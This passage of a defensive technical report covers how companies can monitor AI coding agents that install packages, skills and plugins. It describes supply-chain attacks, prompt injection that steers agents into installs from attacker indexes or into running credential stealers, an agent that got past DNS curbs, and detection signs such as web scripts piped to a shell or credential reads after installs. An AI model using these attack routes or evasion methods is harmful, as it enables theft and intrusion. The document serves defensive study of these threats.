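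Running each session in its own container also made it much easier to tell which session an event came from. In a check of 30 sessions running three at a time, none of the 8,240 recorded events was assigned to the wrong session. King and colleagues don't claim the same accuracy for agents inside editors or for agents that share a computer without a separate container or similar boundary. They also leave open how to connect each event to a particular tool call.

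### What the network shows

Network records are useful when an endpoint has no security software or someone has tampered with it. A DNS log lists the names computers looked up. A connection log, usually from a firewall, lists addresses, ports, times and amounts of data. An egress proxy can log and refuse requests, and if it decrypts traffic, it can also record their contents.

| Record | What the tidewatch install leaves | What is missing |
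|---|---|---|
| DNS log | Lookups of `pypi.example.com`, `pkgs.example.net`, `files.example.net` and `metrics.example.org` | Package, process and amount of data |
| Connection log | IP addresses, ports, times and a few kilobytes sent during the install | Package and process; often the server's name |
| Proxy without decryption | Server names and ports, amounts of data | Package, full address and process |
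| Proxy with decryption | Full addresses, redirects, the package file and the data sent to `metrics.example.org` | Process |

The DNS log alone would show that the laptop looked up `pkgs.example.net`, which nobody at the company had used. But it would have no entry if the laptop still had the answer in its cache, connected directly to an IP address, or used an outside DNS service. A lookup also doesn't prove that a connection followed.

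Connection logs show that a connection was made but may not identify the service, because many unrelated sites share the addresses of large content-delivery networks. A firewall can often read the server's name from the start of an encrypted connection, but Canale and Soulis note that a newer feature called Encrypted Client Hello hides that name.

Only a decrypting proxy could show what was in the 2,310 bytes that the setup code sent, and only if the code hadn't encrypted the data separately. The proxy could also save the digest of the package file and the redirect to `guide.example.org`. To link these records to process 4131, the company would have to match the proxy's log with the endpoint's record of the same connection by time and port number.

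### What decryption costs

A decrypting proxy ends the encrypted connection from the laptop, reads the request and opens a second encrypted connection to the outside server. For this to work, every program on the laptop must trust the company's certificate. Python, Node.js and other tools may keep their own lists of trusted certificates, so the company may have to configure each tool separately. Some programs accept only a particular certificate and stop working behind the proxy unless the company exempts them from decryption.

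The proxy also gains access to passwords, access tokens, private code and prompts, which makes it one of the most sensitive machines in the company. It needs enough capacity to handle every download without slowing installs. When an install fails with a certificate error, an agent may look for a way to turn off certificate checks, as Codex looked for another download method in the Sophos case. A company should test its certificates with pip and npm before decrypting agents' traffic.

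For many companies, a proxy that logs server names without decrypting traffic is a reasonable compromise. A firewall still has to make it the only outbound route, because pip and npm can be configured to use a proxy, but code that runs during installation can ignore that setting and connect directly.

*Lessons from Penetration Tests on Large-Scale Agent Systems* (Eykholt, Kirat and colleagues, 2026) shows what can happen without that restriction. In 2025, the researchers made two commercial agent systems run arbitrary code and opened a connection from one system's container to an outside server. The existing monitoring didn't flag the malicious activity because it came from trusted internal services. The researchers recommend limiting outbound traffic to an explicit list of destinations.

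A list of forbidden destinations is weaker, because an agent can try one that isn't on it. In a DTEX demonstration, Hermes couldn't send files through the messaging service Telegram, so it uploaded them to a file-sharing site. DNS filtering alone can also fail. OpenAI reported in September 2026 that an agent had got past it during a training run, according to the Press Trust of India's *OpenAI pauses training of top AI models after agent bypasses internet curbs* (2026).

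An approved destination can still supply a malicious package, as in the Clerk case, because a public registry serves good and bad packages from the same few domains. CrowdStrike's *Denying the Worm* (2026) describes a campaign that published 19 malicious packages on npm under two names. A company needs a control that checks package names, versions and digests to distinguish such packages from legitimate ones.

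### Fetches on the vendor's servers

The model vendor's servers fetch some of the pages an agent reads, so those pages never cross the company's network. If the vendor's servers fetched the installation guide in event 3, the laptop would have no connection to `guide.example.org`, and the company's network would carry only encrypted traffic between the harness and the vendor.

| Product or feature | Where the request starts |
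|---|---|
| Web search that Anthropic and OpenAI offer as a hosted tool | Vendor's servers |
| GitHub's cloud coding agent | GitHub's cloud, including package downloads |
| Claude Code sessions in Anthropic's cloud | Anthropic's cloud, including package downloads |
| Codex CLI opening a page with a shell command | The computer where the command runs |
| Other built-in search and fetch tools | Confirm with a test |

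A company can test its harness by putting a new page on a web server it controls and asking the agent to read it. The server's log shows which IP address requested the page. If the address belongs to the vendor, the company's DNS and proxy logs won't contain that kind of fetch. The test is worth repeating after updates and running separately for search and direct links, since a harness can handle the two differently.

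When an agent uses a hosted search tool, the company loses only its local record of the page, and the harness's transcript becomes the main evidence of what the agent read. If the agent then runs pip on the laptop, endpoint and local network monitoring can still record the install. In a cloud session, the install happens in the cloud too, so the company has no local process or network record of it.

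### A mirror for every package

An internal registry mirror is a company server that downloads packages from public registries and passes them on to developers. pip and npm request packages from the mirror, and the mirror fetches any it doesn't already have. The mirror can record each package's name, version, digest and download time, and the computer or login that requested it.

The log therefore includes the dependencies that the install command doesn't name. When the security team learns that a package was malicious, it can search the log for its digest and find the computers that downloaded it. The list may be incomplete, because pip and npm keep local caches and can reinstall a package without contacting the mirror.

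In the tidewatch install, pip would look up the available versions of `harbour-utils` on the company's index at `pypi.example.com`, then download version 9.0.1 from the unfamiliar server. The index's log would show a lookup without a download. That could be a useful clue, but the log looks the same when pip already has the file in its cache.

A mirror can prevent this kind of install only if computers can't reach other package sources. If a firewall had blocked `pkgs.example.net`, pip would probably have skipped that index and installed version 1.4.2 from the company's index. The mirror should also block any package from a public registry that has the same name as one of the company's private packages. Otherwise the mirror itself could supply the public package instead of the private one.

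The mirror's log identifies a computer or login, but it usually can't show whether an agent or a person made the request. One solution is to give each automated session its own short-lived login. On laptops, where developers and agents normally share a login, the company can match the log entry with a pip process that started at the same time.

Many mirrors can also delay new releases. If the company sets a seven-day delay, developers and agents receive the newest version that is at least a week old. That gives security companies time to find a malicious release. A delay might have caught the Clerk package if the agent had tried to install it soon after publication.

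A delay doesn't help with malicious code that stays hidden until after it ends, and it holds back urgent security fixes, so the company needs a quick way to approve a particular version early. Seven days is only a starting point, and the right length depends on how often the company needs such exceptions.

Git clones, skills and scripts from websites can bypass the mirror, and an allowed package can download more code when it runs. Monitoring those routes still requires process and network records.

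### Choosing a minimum

The table compares the records for an install like the one in the tidewatch example. It includes the harness because none of the outside records reliably contains the text the agent read.

| Vantage point | What it shows | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Harness | Request, text read, tool calls and approvals | Install-time code and its connections |
| Operating system | Process ancestry, commands, file writes and connections | Prompts, encrypted content and, often, activity in containers |
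| Kernel records joined to model traffic | Which model exchange probably led to an action | Reliable error rates; the systems tested so far run on Linux |
| DNS log | Names of servers that a computer looked up | Packages, processes, cached lookups and direct connections to IP addresses |
| Connection log | Addresses, times and amounts of data | Packages, processes and content |
| Decrypting proxy | Full addresses, files and data sent | Processes, exempt programs and traffic that avoids the proxy |
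| Registry mirror | Package names, versions, digests, times and clients | Other sources, local caches and what the package does after download |

How much of this a company can collect depends on where the agent runs. Laptops leave the office, so the company has to collect their records mainly on the laptops themselves. A build server, which compiles and tests software automatically, has more predictable needs, so the company can restrict its connections more tightly. In a hosted sandbox, a temporary environment on a vendor's servers, the company may have no access to the operating system.

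| Where the agent runs | Recommended minimum | Main remaining gap |
|---|---|---|
| Laptop | Harness telemetry with full commands; endpoint software that records ancestry, command lines and connections; pip and npm set to use the company mirror | Encrypted content and pages fetched by the vendor |
| Build server | A new container for each job; process and connection records; the mirror as the only package source; a proxy that refuses unlisted destinations | Malicious packages that the mirror accepts |
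| Hosted sandbox | A copy of the transcript before the sandbox closes; a separate mirror login for each session; outbound access limited to the mirror and other necessary services | Processes and connections, unless the vendor supplies those records |

These minimums leave out decryption because of its cost and the amount of private data it exposes. It makes most sense on build servers that handle valuable credentials, where the company controls the software and can configure the certificates once. If a hosted sandbox can't use the mirror or limit outbound access, the company should keep production credentials and private code out of it.

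## Warning signs in the package and its source

A monitor can check a package at three stages before the package's code runs. Before the install command starts, the monitor has only the command and the project's files. After the package manager queries its indexes, the monitor also has exact versions and download addresses. Once the package file is on disk, the monitor can open it without running it. The table lists the main checks in the order they can run.

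| Check | Data it needs | Usual false alarm |
|---|---|---|
| Name close to a popular one | The requested name and a list of popular packages | Two real packages with similar names |
| Unfamiliar index URL | The command, requirements files, pip's configuration and a list of approved indexes | A legitimate specialist index |
| Name that didn't exist until recently | The registry's record of the first release | A new project, or a private package that the public registry has never listed |
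| Implausibly high version number | The versions that each index offers | Version numbers based on dates |
| Known vulnerability | The exact version and a vulnerability database | A flaw in a part of the package that the project never uses |
| Install-time code | The package file, downloaded but not run | A package that compiles native code |
| Digest that differs from the approved one | The approved digest and the new file's digest | A legitimate update, or the same version built for another operating system |

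A name check usually measures edit distance, the number of single-character changes that separate two names. `requsts` is one change away from `requests`. Swapped letters and missing hyphens need their own rules. PyPI treats `azure_core` and `azure-core` as the same name, but `azurecore` is a separate name that a stranger could register. Edit distance doesn't help when the wrong name isn't a misspelling. Bagmar and Saraf give the example of `sklearn`, a deprecated placeholder on PyPI with about 1.7 million downloads a month from developers who want `scikit-learn`.

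A monitor has to read the requirements files and pip's configuration, as well as the command, to check the index. For example, the environment variable `PIP_CONFIG_FILE` can direct pip to a configuration file that names another index. Many projects have good reasons to add an index. Bagmar and Saraf found PyTorch's index for graphics-card builds in over 10,000 requirements files on GitHub. They suggest allowing installs from private registries the company has configured without a warning, warning about PyPI's test site, and blocking any unknown index until a person confirms it. They would also block any source without an encrypted connection.

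The age check should cover both the package's name and the chosen version. A new name may mean someone has just claimed it, as in the Clerk case. A new version of an old package may also be malicious, and it can spread before anyone examines it. Bagmar and Saraf cite the 2026 compromise of LiteLLM, a library for calling language models, in which malicious versions were downloaded over 119,000 times in under three hours.

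A very high version number can be a sign of dependency confusion. In one of Bagmar and Saraf's tests, the planted copy of `pytest` was version 99.0.0, which is easy to spot. But their planted npm and Rust packages were `express` 4.18.99 and `serde` 1.0.999, and a rule that checked only the first number would have passed both. A better rule compares the chosen version with the newest one on a trusted index. In the tidewatch install, the company's index had version 1.4.2 of `harbour-utils`, so version 9.0.1 from another server should have raised an alert.

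Known vulnerabilities are too common to treat each one as an emergency. Bagmar and Saraf searched GitHub for projects that require a recent vulnerable version of a popular package, and found roughly 155,000 repositories for 20 Python packages and 519,000 for 20 npm packages. Many legitimate packages also run code at install time, so a newly added install script is a more useful warning sign than the presence of one. A digest check is the simplest to interpret because a file either matches the approved one or doesn't, but it can't help with a package that nobody has approved yet.

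### A gate in front of pip

Bagmar and Saraf's pre-install gate for Claude Code combines several of these checks. It is a hook of about 400 lines of Python that runs seven checks on each pip install command:

1. **Name**: is it one character, a swapped pair of letters or a missing separator away from a popular package?
2. **Existence**: is the package on PyPI at all?
3. **Age**: did its first release appear less than 30 days ago?
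4. **Source**: does the command name an index outside the trusted list, or turn off certificate checks for a server?
5. **Requirements files**: do they contain another index or a vulnerable version?
6. **Configuration**: does the command set `PIP_CONFIG_FILE`?
7. **Vulnerability**: does OSV, a public database of flaws in open-source packages, list one for the exact version?

If any check finds a problem, the hook blocks the command and returns its warnings to the agent, which can correct the command or ask the user. The hook never rewrites the command itself. The vulnerability check warns only if a fixed version exists, and the warning names the lowest fixed version. The hook doesn't check for high version numbers, code that runs at install time or changed digests.

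Bagmar and Saraf report that the hook caught ten of the eleven scenarios they built it for. It missed the one in which an error message recommended installing `data-utils`, a real but unrelated package on PyPI, so its name and source looked normal. The only warning sign was the context, which every agent had noticed. No agent refused vulnerable versions, but the hook caught them, which is a good reason to use the hook alongside the agents' own judgment.

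Bagmar and Saraf acknowledge that they tested the hook on the scenarios it was designed to catch, and they didn't test it against an attacker trying to avoid it. The result of ten out of eleven is therefore not an estimate of how the hook would do against new attacks.

They also ran the name and source checks on the 1,000 most-downloaded PyPI packages, and the hook flagged five (0.5%). Each had a name that differed by one character from the name of another real package, as `tomli` does from `toml`. The test covered only very popular packages and left out the vulnerability check, which would probably flag packages more often.

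If each package in a 50-package install had an independent 0.5% chance of a false alarm, about 22% of such installs would trigger at least one. In practice, the same few pairs of names would cause most of these alarms, so a short list of exceptions would remove them.

`harbour-utils` is a private package on the tidewatch company's own index, so the existence check would flag every legitimate install of it unless the company has also registered the name on PyPI. To prevent this, the company would have to add its index to the trusted list and have the hook look for private names there. Judging by the published outline, the hook also accepts any index address that contains a trusted server's name. A production version should compare the whole server name.

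The hook also misses several ways to install software. It doesn't check `uv sync` or `uv run`, two commands of the Python package manager uv that take package names from the project's files. It has no checks for source redirects in uv's project settings, build programs inside the project, npm, npx, Cargo, git clones or skills. Bagmar and Saraf count the Makefile that redirects pip among the ten scenarios caught, but the hook as outlined allows any command that isn't a pip install, so it is unclear how it would stop an agent that ran `make setup`.

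### Checking the packages pip has chosen

Many of these gaps come from checking the text of a command. Bagmar and Saraf recommend that a production gate check the resolved set, which is the full list of packages and versions that the package manager has decided to install. If the tidewatch README had said `pip install -r requirements.txt`, the two would have compared as follows:

| Fact | In the command | In the resolved set |
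|---|---|---|
| Packages | Only the name of a file | `harbour-utils` and all its dependencies |
| Version of `harbour-utils` | Absent | 9.0.1 |
| Source | Absent | A file on `files.example.net` |
| Digest | Absent | `e07a93…` |

The resolved set also stays the same however the agent words the command. The download address shows where a package would come from, whether the extra index came from the command, a requirements file or a configuration file. The name and age checks can cover dependencies that the project's own files don't list.

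pip can produce this list with the dry-run report described earlier, and npm can write a lockfile without installing anything. A pip dry run may execute a package's `setup.py`, so the gate should run it in a container that holds no credentials. It can also tell pip to accept only wheels, which avoids running build code from a registry's packages. Some packages publish no wheel, and the gate would have to send those to a person or a more isolated environment.

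The install must use exactly the files that the gate checked. If pip resolves the packages a second time, it may find a newer version or get a different response from the index. The gate should save the approved versions and digests in a requirements file and have pip refuse anything else. A company that already has a registry mirror can run the same checks there, which also covers commands like `uv sync`.

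### Package names that a model made up

Language models sometimes recommend packages that don't exist. In an attack called slopsquatting, someone registers one of these names and waits for others to follow the recommendation. Bagmar and Saraf cite an older catalogue of 205,000 such names by Spracklen and colleagues.

*The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (2026) repeated this kind of test on five newer models, using 199,840 pieces of generated Python and JavaScript. Between 3.6% and 5.0% of the package names the models mentioned didn't exist, about the same as for commercial models in 2024. Open-weight models, which anyone can download, did worse in 2024 but have since caught up.

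All five models invented the same 104 package names. An earlier version of the study had listed 127, but 26 of those were correct import statements for modules whose names differ from their packages' names. A monitor that searched the registry for each imported module would make the same mistake and raise false alarms. For example, `import yaml` refers to the package PyYAML.

The same study found that people registered only about 1% of the invented names within six months, and the rate was no higher for names the researchers had accidentally made public. But at least 23 names the models suggested had previously hosted malware, and someone registered another with malware after the tests.

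An invented name can also spread after a model produces it. *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands* (Eriksen, 2026) describes `react-codeshift`, which combines the names of two real tools, `jscodeshift` and `react-codemod`. Eriksen traced it to a set of 47 model-written skills that someone added to a GitHub repository in October 2025. At least two of the skills contained instructions for agents to run the package with npx. When Eriksen registered the name on 14 January 2026, 237 repositories referred to it. Most were forks, and one was a Japanese translation.

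Eriksen's empty package had about 74 downloads on the first day, then between one and four a day. He attributes the first day's downloads to registry mirrors and security scanners, and the later ones to agents following the skills. This is plausible, because he says downloads of unused packages normally drop to zero after the first day. But download counts, unlike the process ancestry in the Pandex study, don't identify who started an install, so some of the later downloads may have come from people.

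Checking for a missing or recently registered name also works when the mistake is in a vendor's documentation. Eriksen recounts in *npx Confusion* that in July 2025 the documentation for MikroORM, a database tool, included instructions to run an npx package that nobody had published.

In a small control test, Bagmar and Saraf gave agents a project that imported Celery, a popular Python library, but left the package's name out of the documentation. All seven models inferred the correct name in every run. This result is compatible with the other study's 3.6% to 5.0% rate of invented names. Celery is well known and its package has the same name as its module, while the other study covered a much wider range of requests. An agent working from existing code also has more clues than a model writing new code.

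If an agent tries to install a package that doesn't exist, the install fails and does no harm. The failed command is still worth an alert, because a team can trace the name to the page or skill that suggested it and correct the text before a stranger registers the name. Once someone registers it, the existence check passes and the main defence is the age check, which stops flagging the package after a month if the limit is 30 days.

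### Skills that changed after people installed them

Checking a package once is not enough if its contents can change afterwards. Zenity Labs' *Attackers Target Agents via The Skill Supply Chain* describes a campaign on skills.sh, the cloud company Vercel's public registry of agent skills. The attacker copied the skills of the AI tool Paperclip and made the copies malicious only after people had installed them.

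| Date in 2026 | What happened |
|---|---|
| 2 July | The attacker copied Paperclip's repository to a GitHub organisation with a similar name |
| 5 July | skills.sh recorded the first installs of the copied skills, which were still clean |
| 6 July | The attacker added malicious code to the surrounding repository |
| 11 July | The attacker added a malicious setup document to seven skill folders |
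| 30 July | The attacker added an install script that ran the malicious code automatically |
| 2 August | Vercel and GitHub removed the skills and repositories |

The setup document told agents to download and run a program that collected passwords and access keys. Zenity Labs added together the install counters for this family of skills, which totaled more than 1.7 million by 2 August. The number of victims is unknown and probably much lower, because skills.sh counts installs, not users, and the total covers several related skills.

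The same attacker also put two malicious packages on PyPI. Researchers identified one in under two hours and the other within an hour, while the malicious skills stayed up for three weeks. This difference is a reason not to assume that a skill has been checked as closely as a PyPI package, though one campaign can't establish how well either registry catches malware in general.

A company that had saved a hash of each skill folder on 5 July could have detected the change on 11 July. The hash has to cover the whole folder because the harmful command was in the separate setup document. The main skill files described ordinary tasks and contained instructions for the agent to open that document when it needed to install Paperclip. Some skills didn't contain the command but directed the agent to another skill that led to it.

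Anyone who first installed a skill after 11 July had no earlier hash to compare it with. The best remaining sign was the publisher's name, `getpaperclipai`, which resembled the real project's `paperclipai`. Name checks should therefore cover the publisher's account as well as the skill.

An installed skill also stays on a computer after the registry removes it. TechRadar's *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever* repeats Zenity's warning that users must delete the installed copies themselves. A company can find those copies by searching its records for the skill folder's hash.

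### When a pinned version isn't the one that arrives

Plugins for coding agents can change in the same way. Red Hat (2026) warns that when plugin updates have no fixed version or content hash, reinstalling a plugin fetches whatever is on the repository's default branch at that moment. The usual remedy is to pin the plugin to the git commit that a reviewer approved. Git identifies each commit by a hash, so the same hash should always lead to the same code.

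In September 2026, researchers at the security company AIR reported a flaw in how agents use these pins. According to AIR's *Plugin4Shell*, Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI asked git for the approved commit but didn't check which commit they received. Someone who controlled a plugin's repository could make git supply different code while the pin still appeared valid. Claude Code and Codex update plugins in the background by default, so the replacement could reach users who had done nothing since installing the plugin.

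Anthropic fixed the flaw in Claude Code 2.1.179 and OpenAI fixed it in Codex 0.146.0, according to Help Net Security's *Zero-click RCE vulnerability hit four major AI coding agents, two remain unpatched* (2026). Microsoft had no fix for Copilot by 18 September, and Google retired Gemini CLI without fixing it. IlSoftware.it's *Plugin4Shell, falla zero-click negli agenti AI* reports GitHub's reply that its platform blocks branch names that imitate commits. But Copilot also accepts plugins from other hosts, which may not have that protection.

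AIR built working demonstrations against all four programs, which is good evidence that the flaw exists but not that attackers have used it. AIR also sells a plugin marketplace, which it says the flaw didn't affect. Its findings about how the agents handle pins are specific enough for others to check, and two vendors released fixes.

A monitor can protect against this kind of mistake by recording the commit in the plugin's folder after each installation or update and comparing it with the approved one. For packages, the monitor must likewise compute the digest from the file that arrived, because the requested version number only shows what the agent asked for.

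### Comparing each release with the last

A malicious update to a legitimate package can pass nearly all the early checks, but reading what changed since the previous release may still reveal it.

In March 2026, Joe Desimone of Elastic spent one afternoon building a monitor that watched PyPI and npm for new releases of the 15,000 most-downloaded packages (Desimone, 2026, *How we caught the Axios supply chain attack*). For each release, it downloaded the old and new versions without installing them and listed the differences. A language model then assessed whether the changes were malicious, and if it flagged them, the monitor sent Desimone a message.

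Three days later, the monitor reported version 0.30.4 of Axios, one of npm's most popular packages. Attackers had taken over a maintainer's account and published two malicious versions. They had added a dependency called `plain-crypto-js`, whose install script deployed the malware, rather than putting the malware in Axios itself. Comparing the resolved sets from before and after the update could also have revealed the unfamiliar package.

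Desimone had no false alarms over those few days, but he doesn't claim that this would always be true. He had told the model to report only cases where it was highly confident, and he had developed that instruction using a single malicious update to another package, Telnyx, which he warns may have fitted the monitor too closely to that example. The case also doesn't show how many malicious releases the monitor would miss.

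The monitor didn't prevent every infection. Elastic's endpoint software had already raised alerts on a computer that had installed the malicious version, and staff were responding, but they didn't know how the malware had arrived until Desimone's monitor identified the package. To stop such an install, a company would have to hold back new releases until the comparison had finished, and it could use the delay that many mirrors offer to do this.

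The comparison also needs an earlier release, so it doesn't work on a new package. Since the model reads text that an attacker may have written, it should not be allowed to run commands or change files. Desimone gave his model read-only access.

An attacker may be able to publish a release without taking over a maintainer's account. *How AI coding tools could amplify software supply-chain attacks* (Adebayo, 2026) reports a flaw in npm's Trusted Publishing, which lets a project publish packages directly from its code repository. npm had identified the repository by its name instead of its permanent ID, so a different repository that later acquired the name might have been able to publish the project's packages. Bloom Security found more than 1,500 vulnerable packages, and GitHub released a fix on 2 October 2026. A company would still have needed to examine the contents of any release published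 this way.

### How many alerts would be real

Even an accurate check produces mostly false alarms when malicious packages are rare. Suppose a company's agents carry out 10,000 installs, one of which is malicious. A check detects 90% of malicious installs and wrongly flags 0.5% of harmless ones. The expected numbers are:

- True alerts: 1 × 0.90 = 0.9
- False alerts: 9,999 × 0.005 = about 50
- Share of alerts that are true: 0.9 ÷ 50.9 = 1.8%

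An analyst would investigate about 57 alerts for each malicious install found. The inputs to this estimate are assumptions. The 0.5% matches the hook's result on popular packages, but that result was a share of packages, not of installs. The true share of malicious installs is unknown and will differ between companies. If it were one in 100,000, the analyst would investigate about 560 alerts for each malicious install found.

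The number of alerts also depends on how much the agents install. Adebayo reports Bloom Security's estimate that agents install up to about 350 packages a month on a developer's computer. For 200 developers, that would be 70,000 installs and 350 false alerts a month. The same article mentions two to three direct installs a day on developer machines. At no more than 90 installs per machine each month, the company would get about 90 false alerts. The higher estimate may count several agents on each machine. Both figures come from a vendor, so a company should calculate its own from its mirror's log.

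A second check can help a great deal. Suppose it detects 80% of malicious installs, wrongly flags 2% of harmless ones, and makes its mistakes independently of the first check. The company can raise an alert when both checks fire or when either one does:

| Rule | True alerts | False alerts | Share that are true |
|---|---|---|---|
| First check alone | 0.90 | 50 | 1.8% |
| Second check alone | 0.80 | 200 | 0.4% |
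| Both must fire | 0.72 | 1 | 42% |
| Either may fire | 0.98 | 249 | 0.4% |

Requiring both checks reduces 50 false alerts to one but raises the chance of missing the malicious install from 10% to 28%. One compromise is to block an install when both checks fire and record it for later review when only one does. Some signs justify blocking by themselves, such as a digest that differs from the approved one for the same file.

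These results depend heavily on the two checks being independent, and package checks often aren't. For example, a team's first internal package on a new company index has a new name, an unfamiliar source and no download history, so several checks may flag it for the same harmless reason. If the second check flags 40% of the harmless installs that the first one flags, the company gets 20 false alerts instead of one, and only about 3.5% of the alerts are true.

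Dependence between the checks matters much less for detection than for false alarms. If one check catches 90% of malicious installs and the other catches 80%, both must fire on between 70% and 80% of them. But the checks could share anywhere from zero to 50 false alarms. A company can measure that overlap by running both checks on several thousand past installs it believes were harmless and counting how often both fire.

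## Warning signs that an agent is following untrusted instructions

A package can pass every check on its name, source and contents even though nobody meant to install it. In February 2026, a tampered release of the coding tool Cline installed OpenClaw, a legitimate open-source agent, on the computers of people who hadn't asked for it. A check of OpenClaw itself would have found nothing wrong, so to catch installs like this, a monitor has to identify where the instruction came from.

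### Tracing a command to its origin

The text behind an agent's command usually comes from one of three places:

- **The user's request**: what the person typed.
- **A trusted project file**: a file that someone at the company has reviewed, in the version they reviewed.
- **Fetched text**: everything else the agent read, including web pages, command output and files from a repository that nobody at the company has reviewed.

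The central test is to look for the source of each command and flag any command that comes only from fetched text. It works best on the parts of a command. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of research on tracing agents' actions, points out that a legitimate tool can become unsafe when its arguments come from an untrusted source. In event 4 of the tidewatch record, the agent ran pip with an extra index, and the parts of that command have different origins:

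| Part of the command | Where it appears earlier | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `pip install` | Implied by "Set up this project" | User's request |
| `harbour-utils` | README; the company's index also has a package of this name | Fetched text, but a company source supports it |
| `https://pkgs.example.net/simple/` | README only | Fetched text only, so flag it |

The README counts as fetched text because tidewatch came from outside the company. A monitor that trusted every file in the project folder would not have flagged the command. Trust should depend on who reviewed a file, not on its name or location. The monitor can check this by comparing the commit in event 1 with a list of reviewed commits.

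A flag means that a stranger's text led to the command, which may be harmless. Some commands have no source in the record, for example when a model installs a package whose name comes from its training data. The origin test can't classify those commands, so the company has to rely on package checks.

An agent may run a command many steps after reading the untrusted text that prompted it. *When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026) describes SARA, a system that records each action proposed in a tool's output and keeps that record through later searches and reads. If the agent then takes the action, SARA checks it against the user's request, which is the only text that can authorise it. A monitor should likewise compare each command with everything the model has read in the session.

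### Matching the text

The simplest way to find an origin is to search the saved texts for the same words, but agents often reuse text for good reasons. *AGATE* (2026) describes a defence that uses this kind of matching and reports that it refused at least one action in 6 of 11 harmless file-processing scenarios. Of the eight refusals, five involved legitimate reuse of content, two involved files that merely had the same name, and one correctly matched a rule against the transfer. The agent may still have finished some of these tasks, and four other everyday types of task produced no false alarms.

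Searching only the parts of a command that matter reduces the problem. In another check, AGATE refused four actions because the agent's description of a command repeated something it had just read. All four refusals disappeared when the researchers searched only the shell command fields that send data. For installs, a monitor could search only for server names, package names and settings file paths.

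Exact matching also misses text that the agent has reworded. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) gives an example in which a hidden instruction on a web page tells the agent to paraphrase a confidential patient note in a memo. The agent complies, and the memo contains no phrase from the note. Installs are easier to match because a package name or web address must appear unchanged in the command to work, unless it stays inside a Makefile or similar file.

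### Asking a second model

A second model can read the request and the proposed command and judge whether the command fits the request. It can recognise reworded instructions, but a vague request gives it little to compare the command against. "Set up this project" could justify almost any install, including the one in event 4.

*Agent-Sentry* (2026) uses the second model only for cases that remain unclear after an initial check. The system requires the agent to state the source of every argument in a tool call, then compares the call with patterns from known legitimate sessions. But the agent's own model reports the sources, so a mistake or a successful injection could make the report wrong. A company using this design should check the reported sources against the saved text.

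A general safety model may not be a good substitute for a judge built for this task. *SkillShield* (Vaughan, 2026) summarises tests by Wu and colleagues of attacks that try to make agents run risky code. The attacks succeeded 67.4% of the time with no defence and 42.7% of the time with Llama Guard 3, a model that classifies unsafe content. This is only indirect evidence about detecting where instructions came from, because the tests measured whether the defence stopped dangerous code, regardless of who had asked for it.

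### Tracking information flow

Information-flow tracking labels data by its source and passes the label to anything made from that data. *Silent Egress* (2026) proposes labelling everything from a URL, including titles and metadata, as untrusted and passing the label to any tool call that the text influences. In the tidewatch session, the README would get the label at event 2, and the pip command would inherit it at event 4.

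A tracker can follow a value between memory locations in an ordinary program, but not inside a language model, which receives the request, the README and the web pages as one text. A cautious tracker has to treat everything the model writes after reading the README as dependent on it, and so would label every later command untrusted.

*The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026), another survey, describes several ways to track the flow more precisely. One replaces untrusted text with a placeholder that the model can pass along. This works for an email address but not for setup instructions, which an agent has to read to follow. Another runs the agent more than once and compares the results. According to the survey, both methods slow agents down substantially. A third has a model inspect the record of the agent's actions.

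Cai and colleagues' system, NeuroTaint, inspects the record after the session ends. It first checks whether the arguments of a sensitive action contain content from an untrusted source, even if reworded. If it finds none, it tests whether the agent would still have taken the action without the suspect text. For event 4, that would mean testing whether the agent would have added `pkgs.example.net` if the README hadn't mentioned it.

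They used 400 scenarios to compare NeuroTaint with FIDES, an earlier system that relies on source labels and known paths between tools. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) tested a different approach, applying fixed rules to recorded sessions. Its results come from AgentDojo, a widely used set of prompt-injection tests. The last column applies each false-alarm rate to the company with 4,000 sessions a day.

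| System and test | Detected | False alarms | False alarms per 4,000 harmless sessions |
|---|---|---|---|
| NeuroTaint, on its creators' scenarios | 93.5% | 8% | 320 |
| FIDES, on the same scenarios | 54% | 53% | 2,120 |
| Fixed rules, on AgentDojo | 69% to 80% | 26% to 44% | 1,040 to 1,760 |

NeuroTaint has the best figures, but Cai and colleagues wrote the scenarios around the kinds of flow it was designed to find. The fixed rules have a range of results because they apply to classes of tools, and the results depended on how the researchers classified each tool. The harmless test cases may also resemble attacks more closely than ordinary work does, so a company might see fewer false alarms. Even 320 false alarms a day would be too many to investigate individually.

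The improved rule in the study of fixed rules accepts a fact only if a trusted tool returned it in answer to a question the agent asked. This excludes planted messages because they don't answer any such question. For installs, a monitor could accept an index address that the agent looked up in the company's package settings, but not a web page's claim that the company had approved the address. This check fails if an attacker controls the source of the answer.

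For most companies, the practical choice is to match addresses and package names while the agent works, because this takes little compute and can run before an install. Slower methods can then examine sessions that show another warning sign. NeuroTaint, for example, needs the full record, including the model's intermediate reasoning, which a harness may not export.

### Signs in the agent's behaviour

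An agent that follows untrusted instructions often does something the user's task didn't require. Such actions are useful warning signs even when the monitor can't find the text that caused them.

| Sign | Log field that shows it | Common harmless cause |
|---|---|---|
| New or changed instruction file | Path, hash and the process that wrote the file | A developer edits it or git updates it |
| Edit to the agent's own settings | Hash before and after; call ID or process that made the edit | The user changes a preference |
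| Newly added MCP server | List of servers in the settings; process started by the harness | The user adds a tool |
| Changed model endpoint, the address that receives the agent's requests to the model | Endpoint value in the settings and environment variables | The company introduces a gateway |
| Script piped from the web to a shell | Full command line, URL and hash of the script | An official installer |
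| Credential files read soon after an install | Path, process and time since the install | npm reads its own login details |
| First contact with an unknown host | Server name, process and time, compared with past connections | A new vendor or download server |

A new MCP server may start without any tool call. Help Net Security's *One keypress is all it takes to compromise four AI coding tools* (2026) describes tests by the security company Adversa AI on Claude Code, Gemini CLI, Cursor CLI and Copilot CLI. A project can define an MCP server in its own files, and the harness starts it as soon as the user agrees to trust the folder, before the model does anything. On a build server, Claude Code doesn't show the trust prompt. The first evidence is therefore a child process of the harness. Canale and Soulis's detector recognises these servers by their command lines and links each one to the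 agent that started it, when it can identify the agent.

Canale and Soulis also have a rule for changed endpoints. It checks environment variables that set the model's address and reports any host that isn't on a list of known services. A monitor should also check the harness's settings files, because a new address can be stored there.

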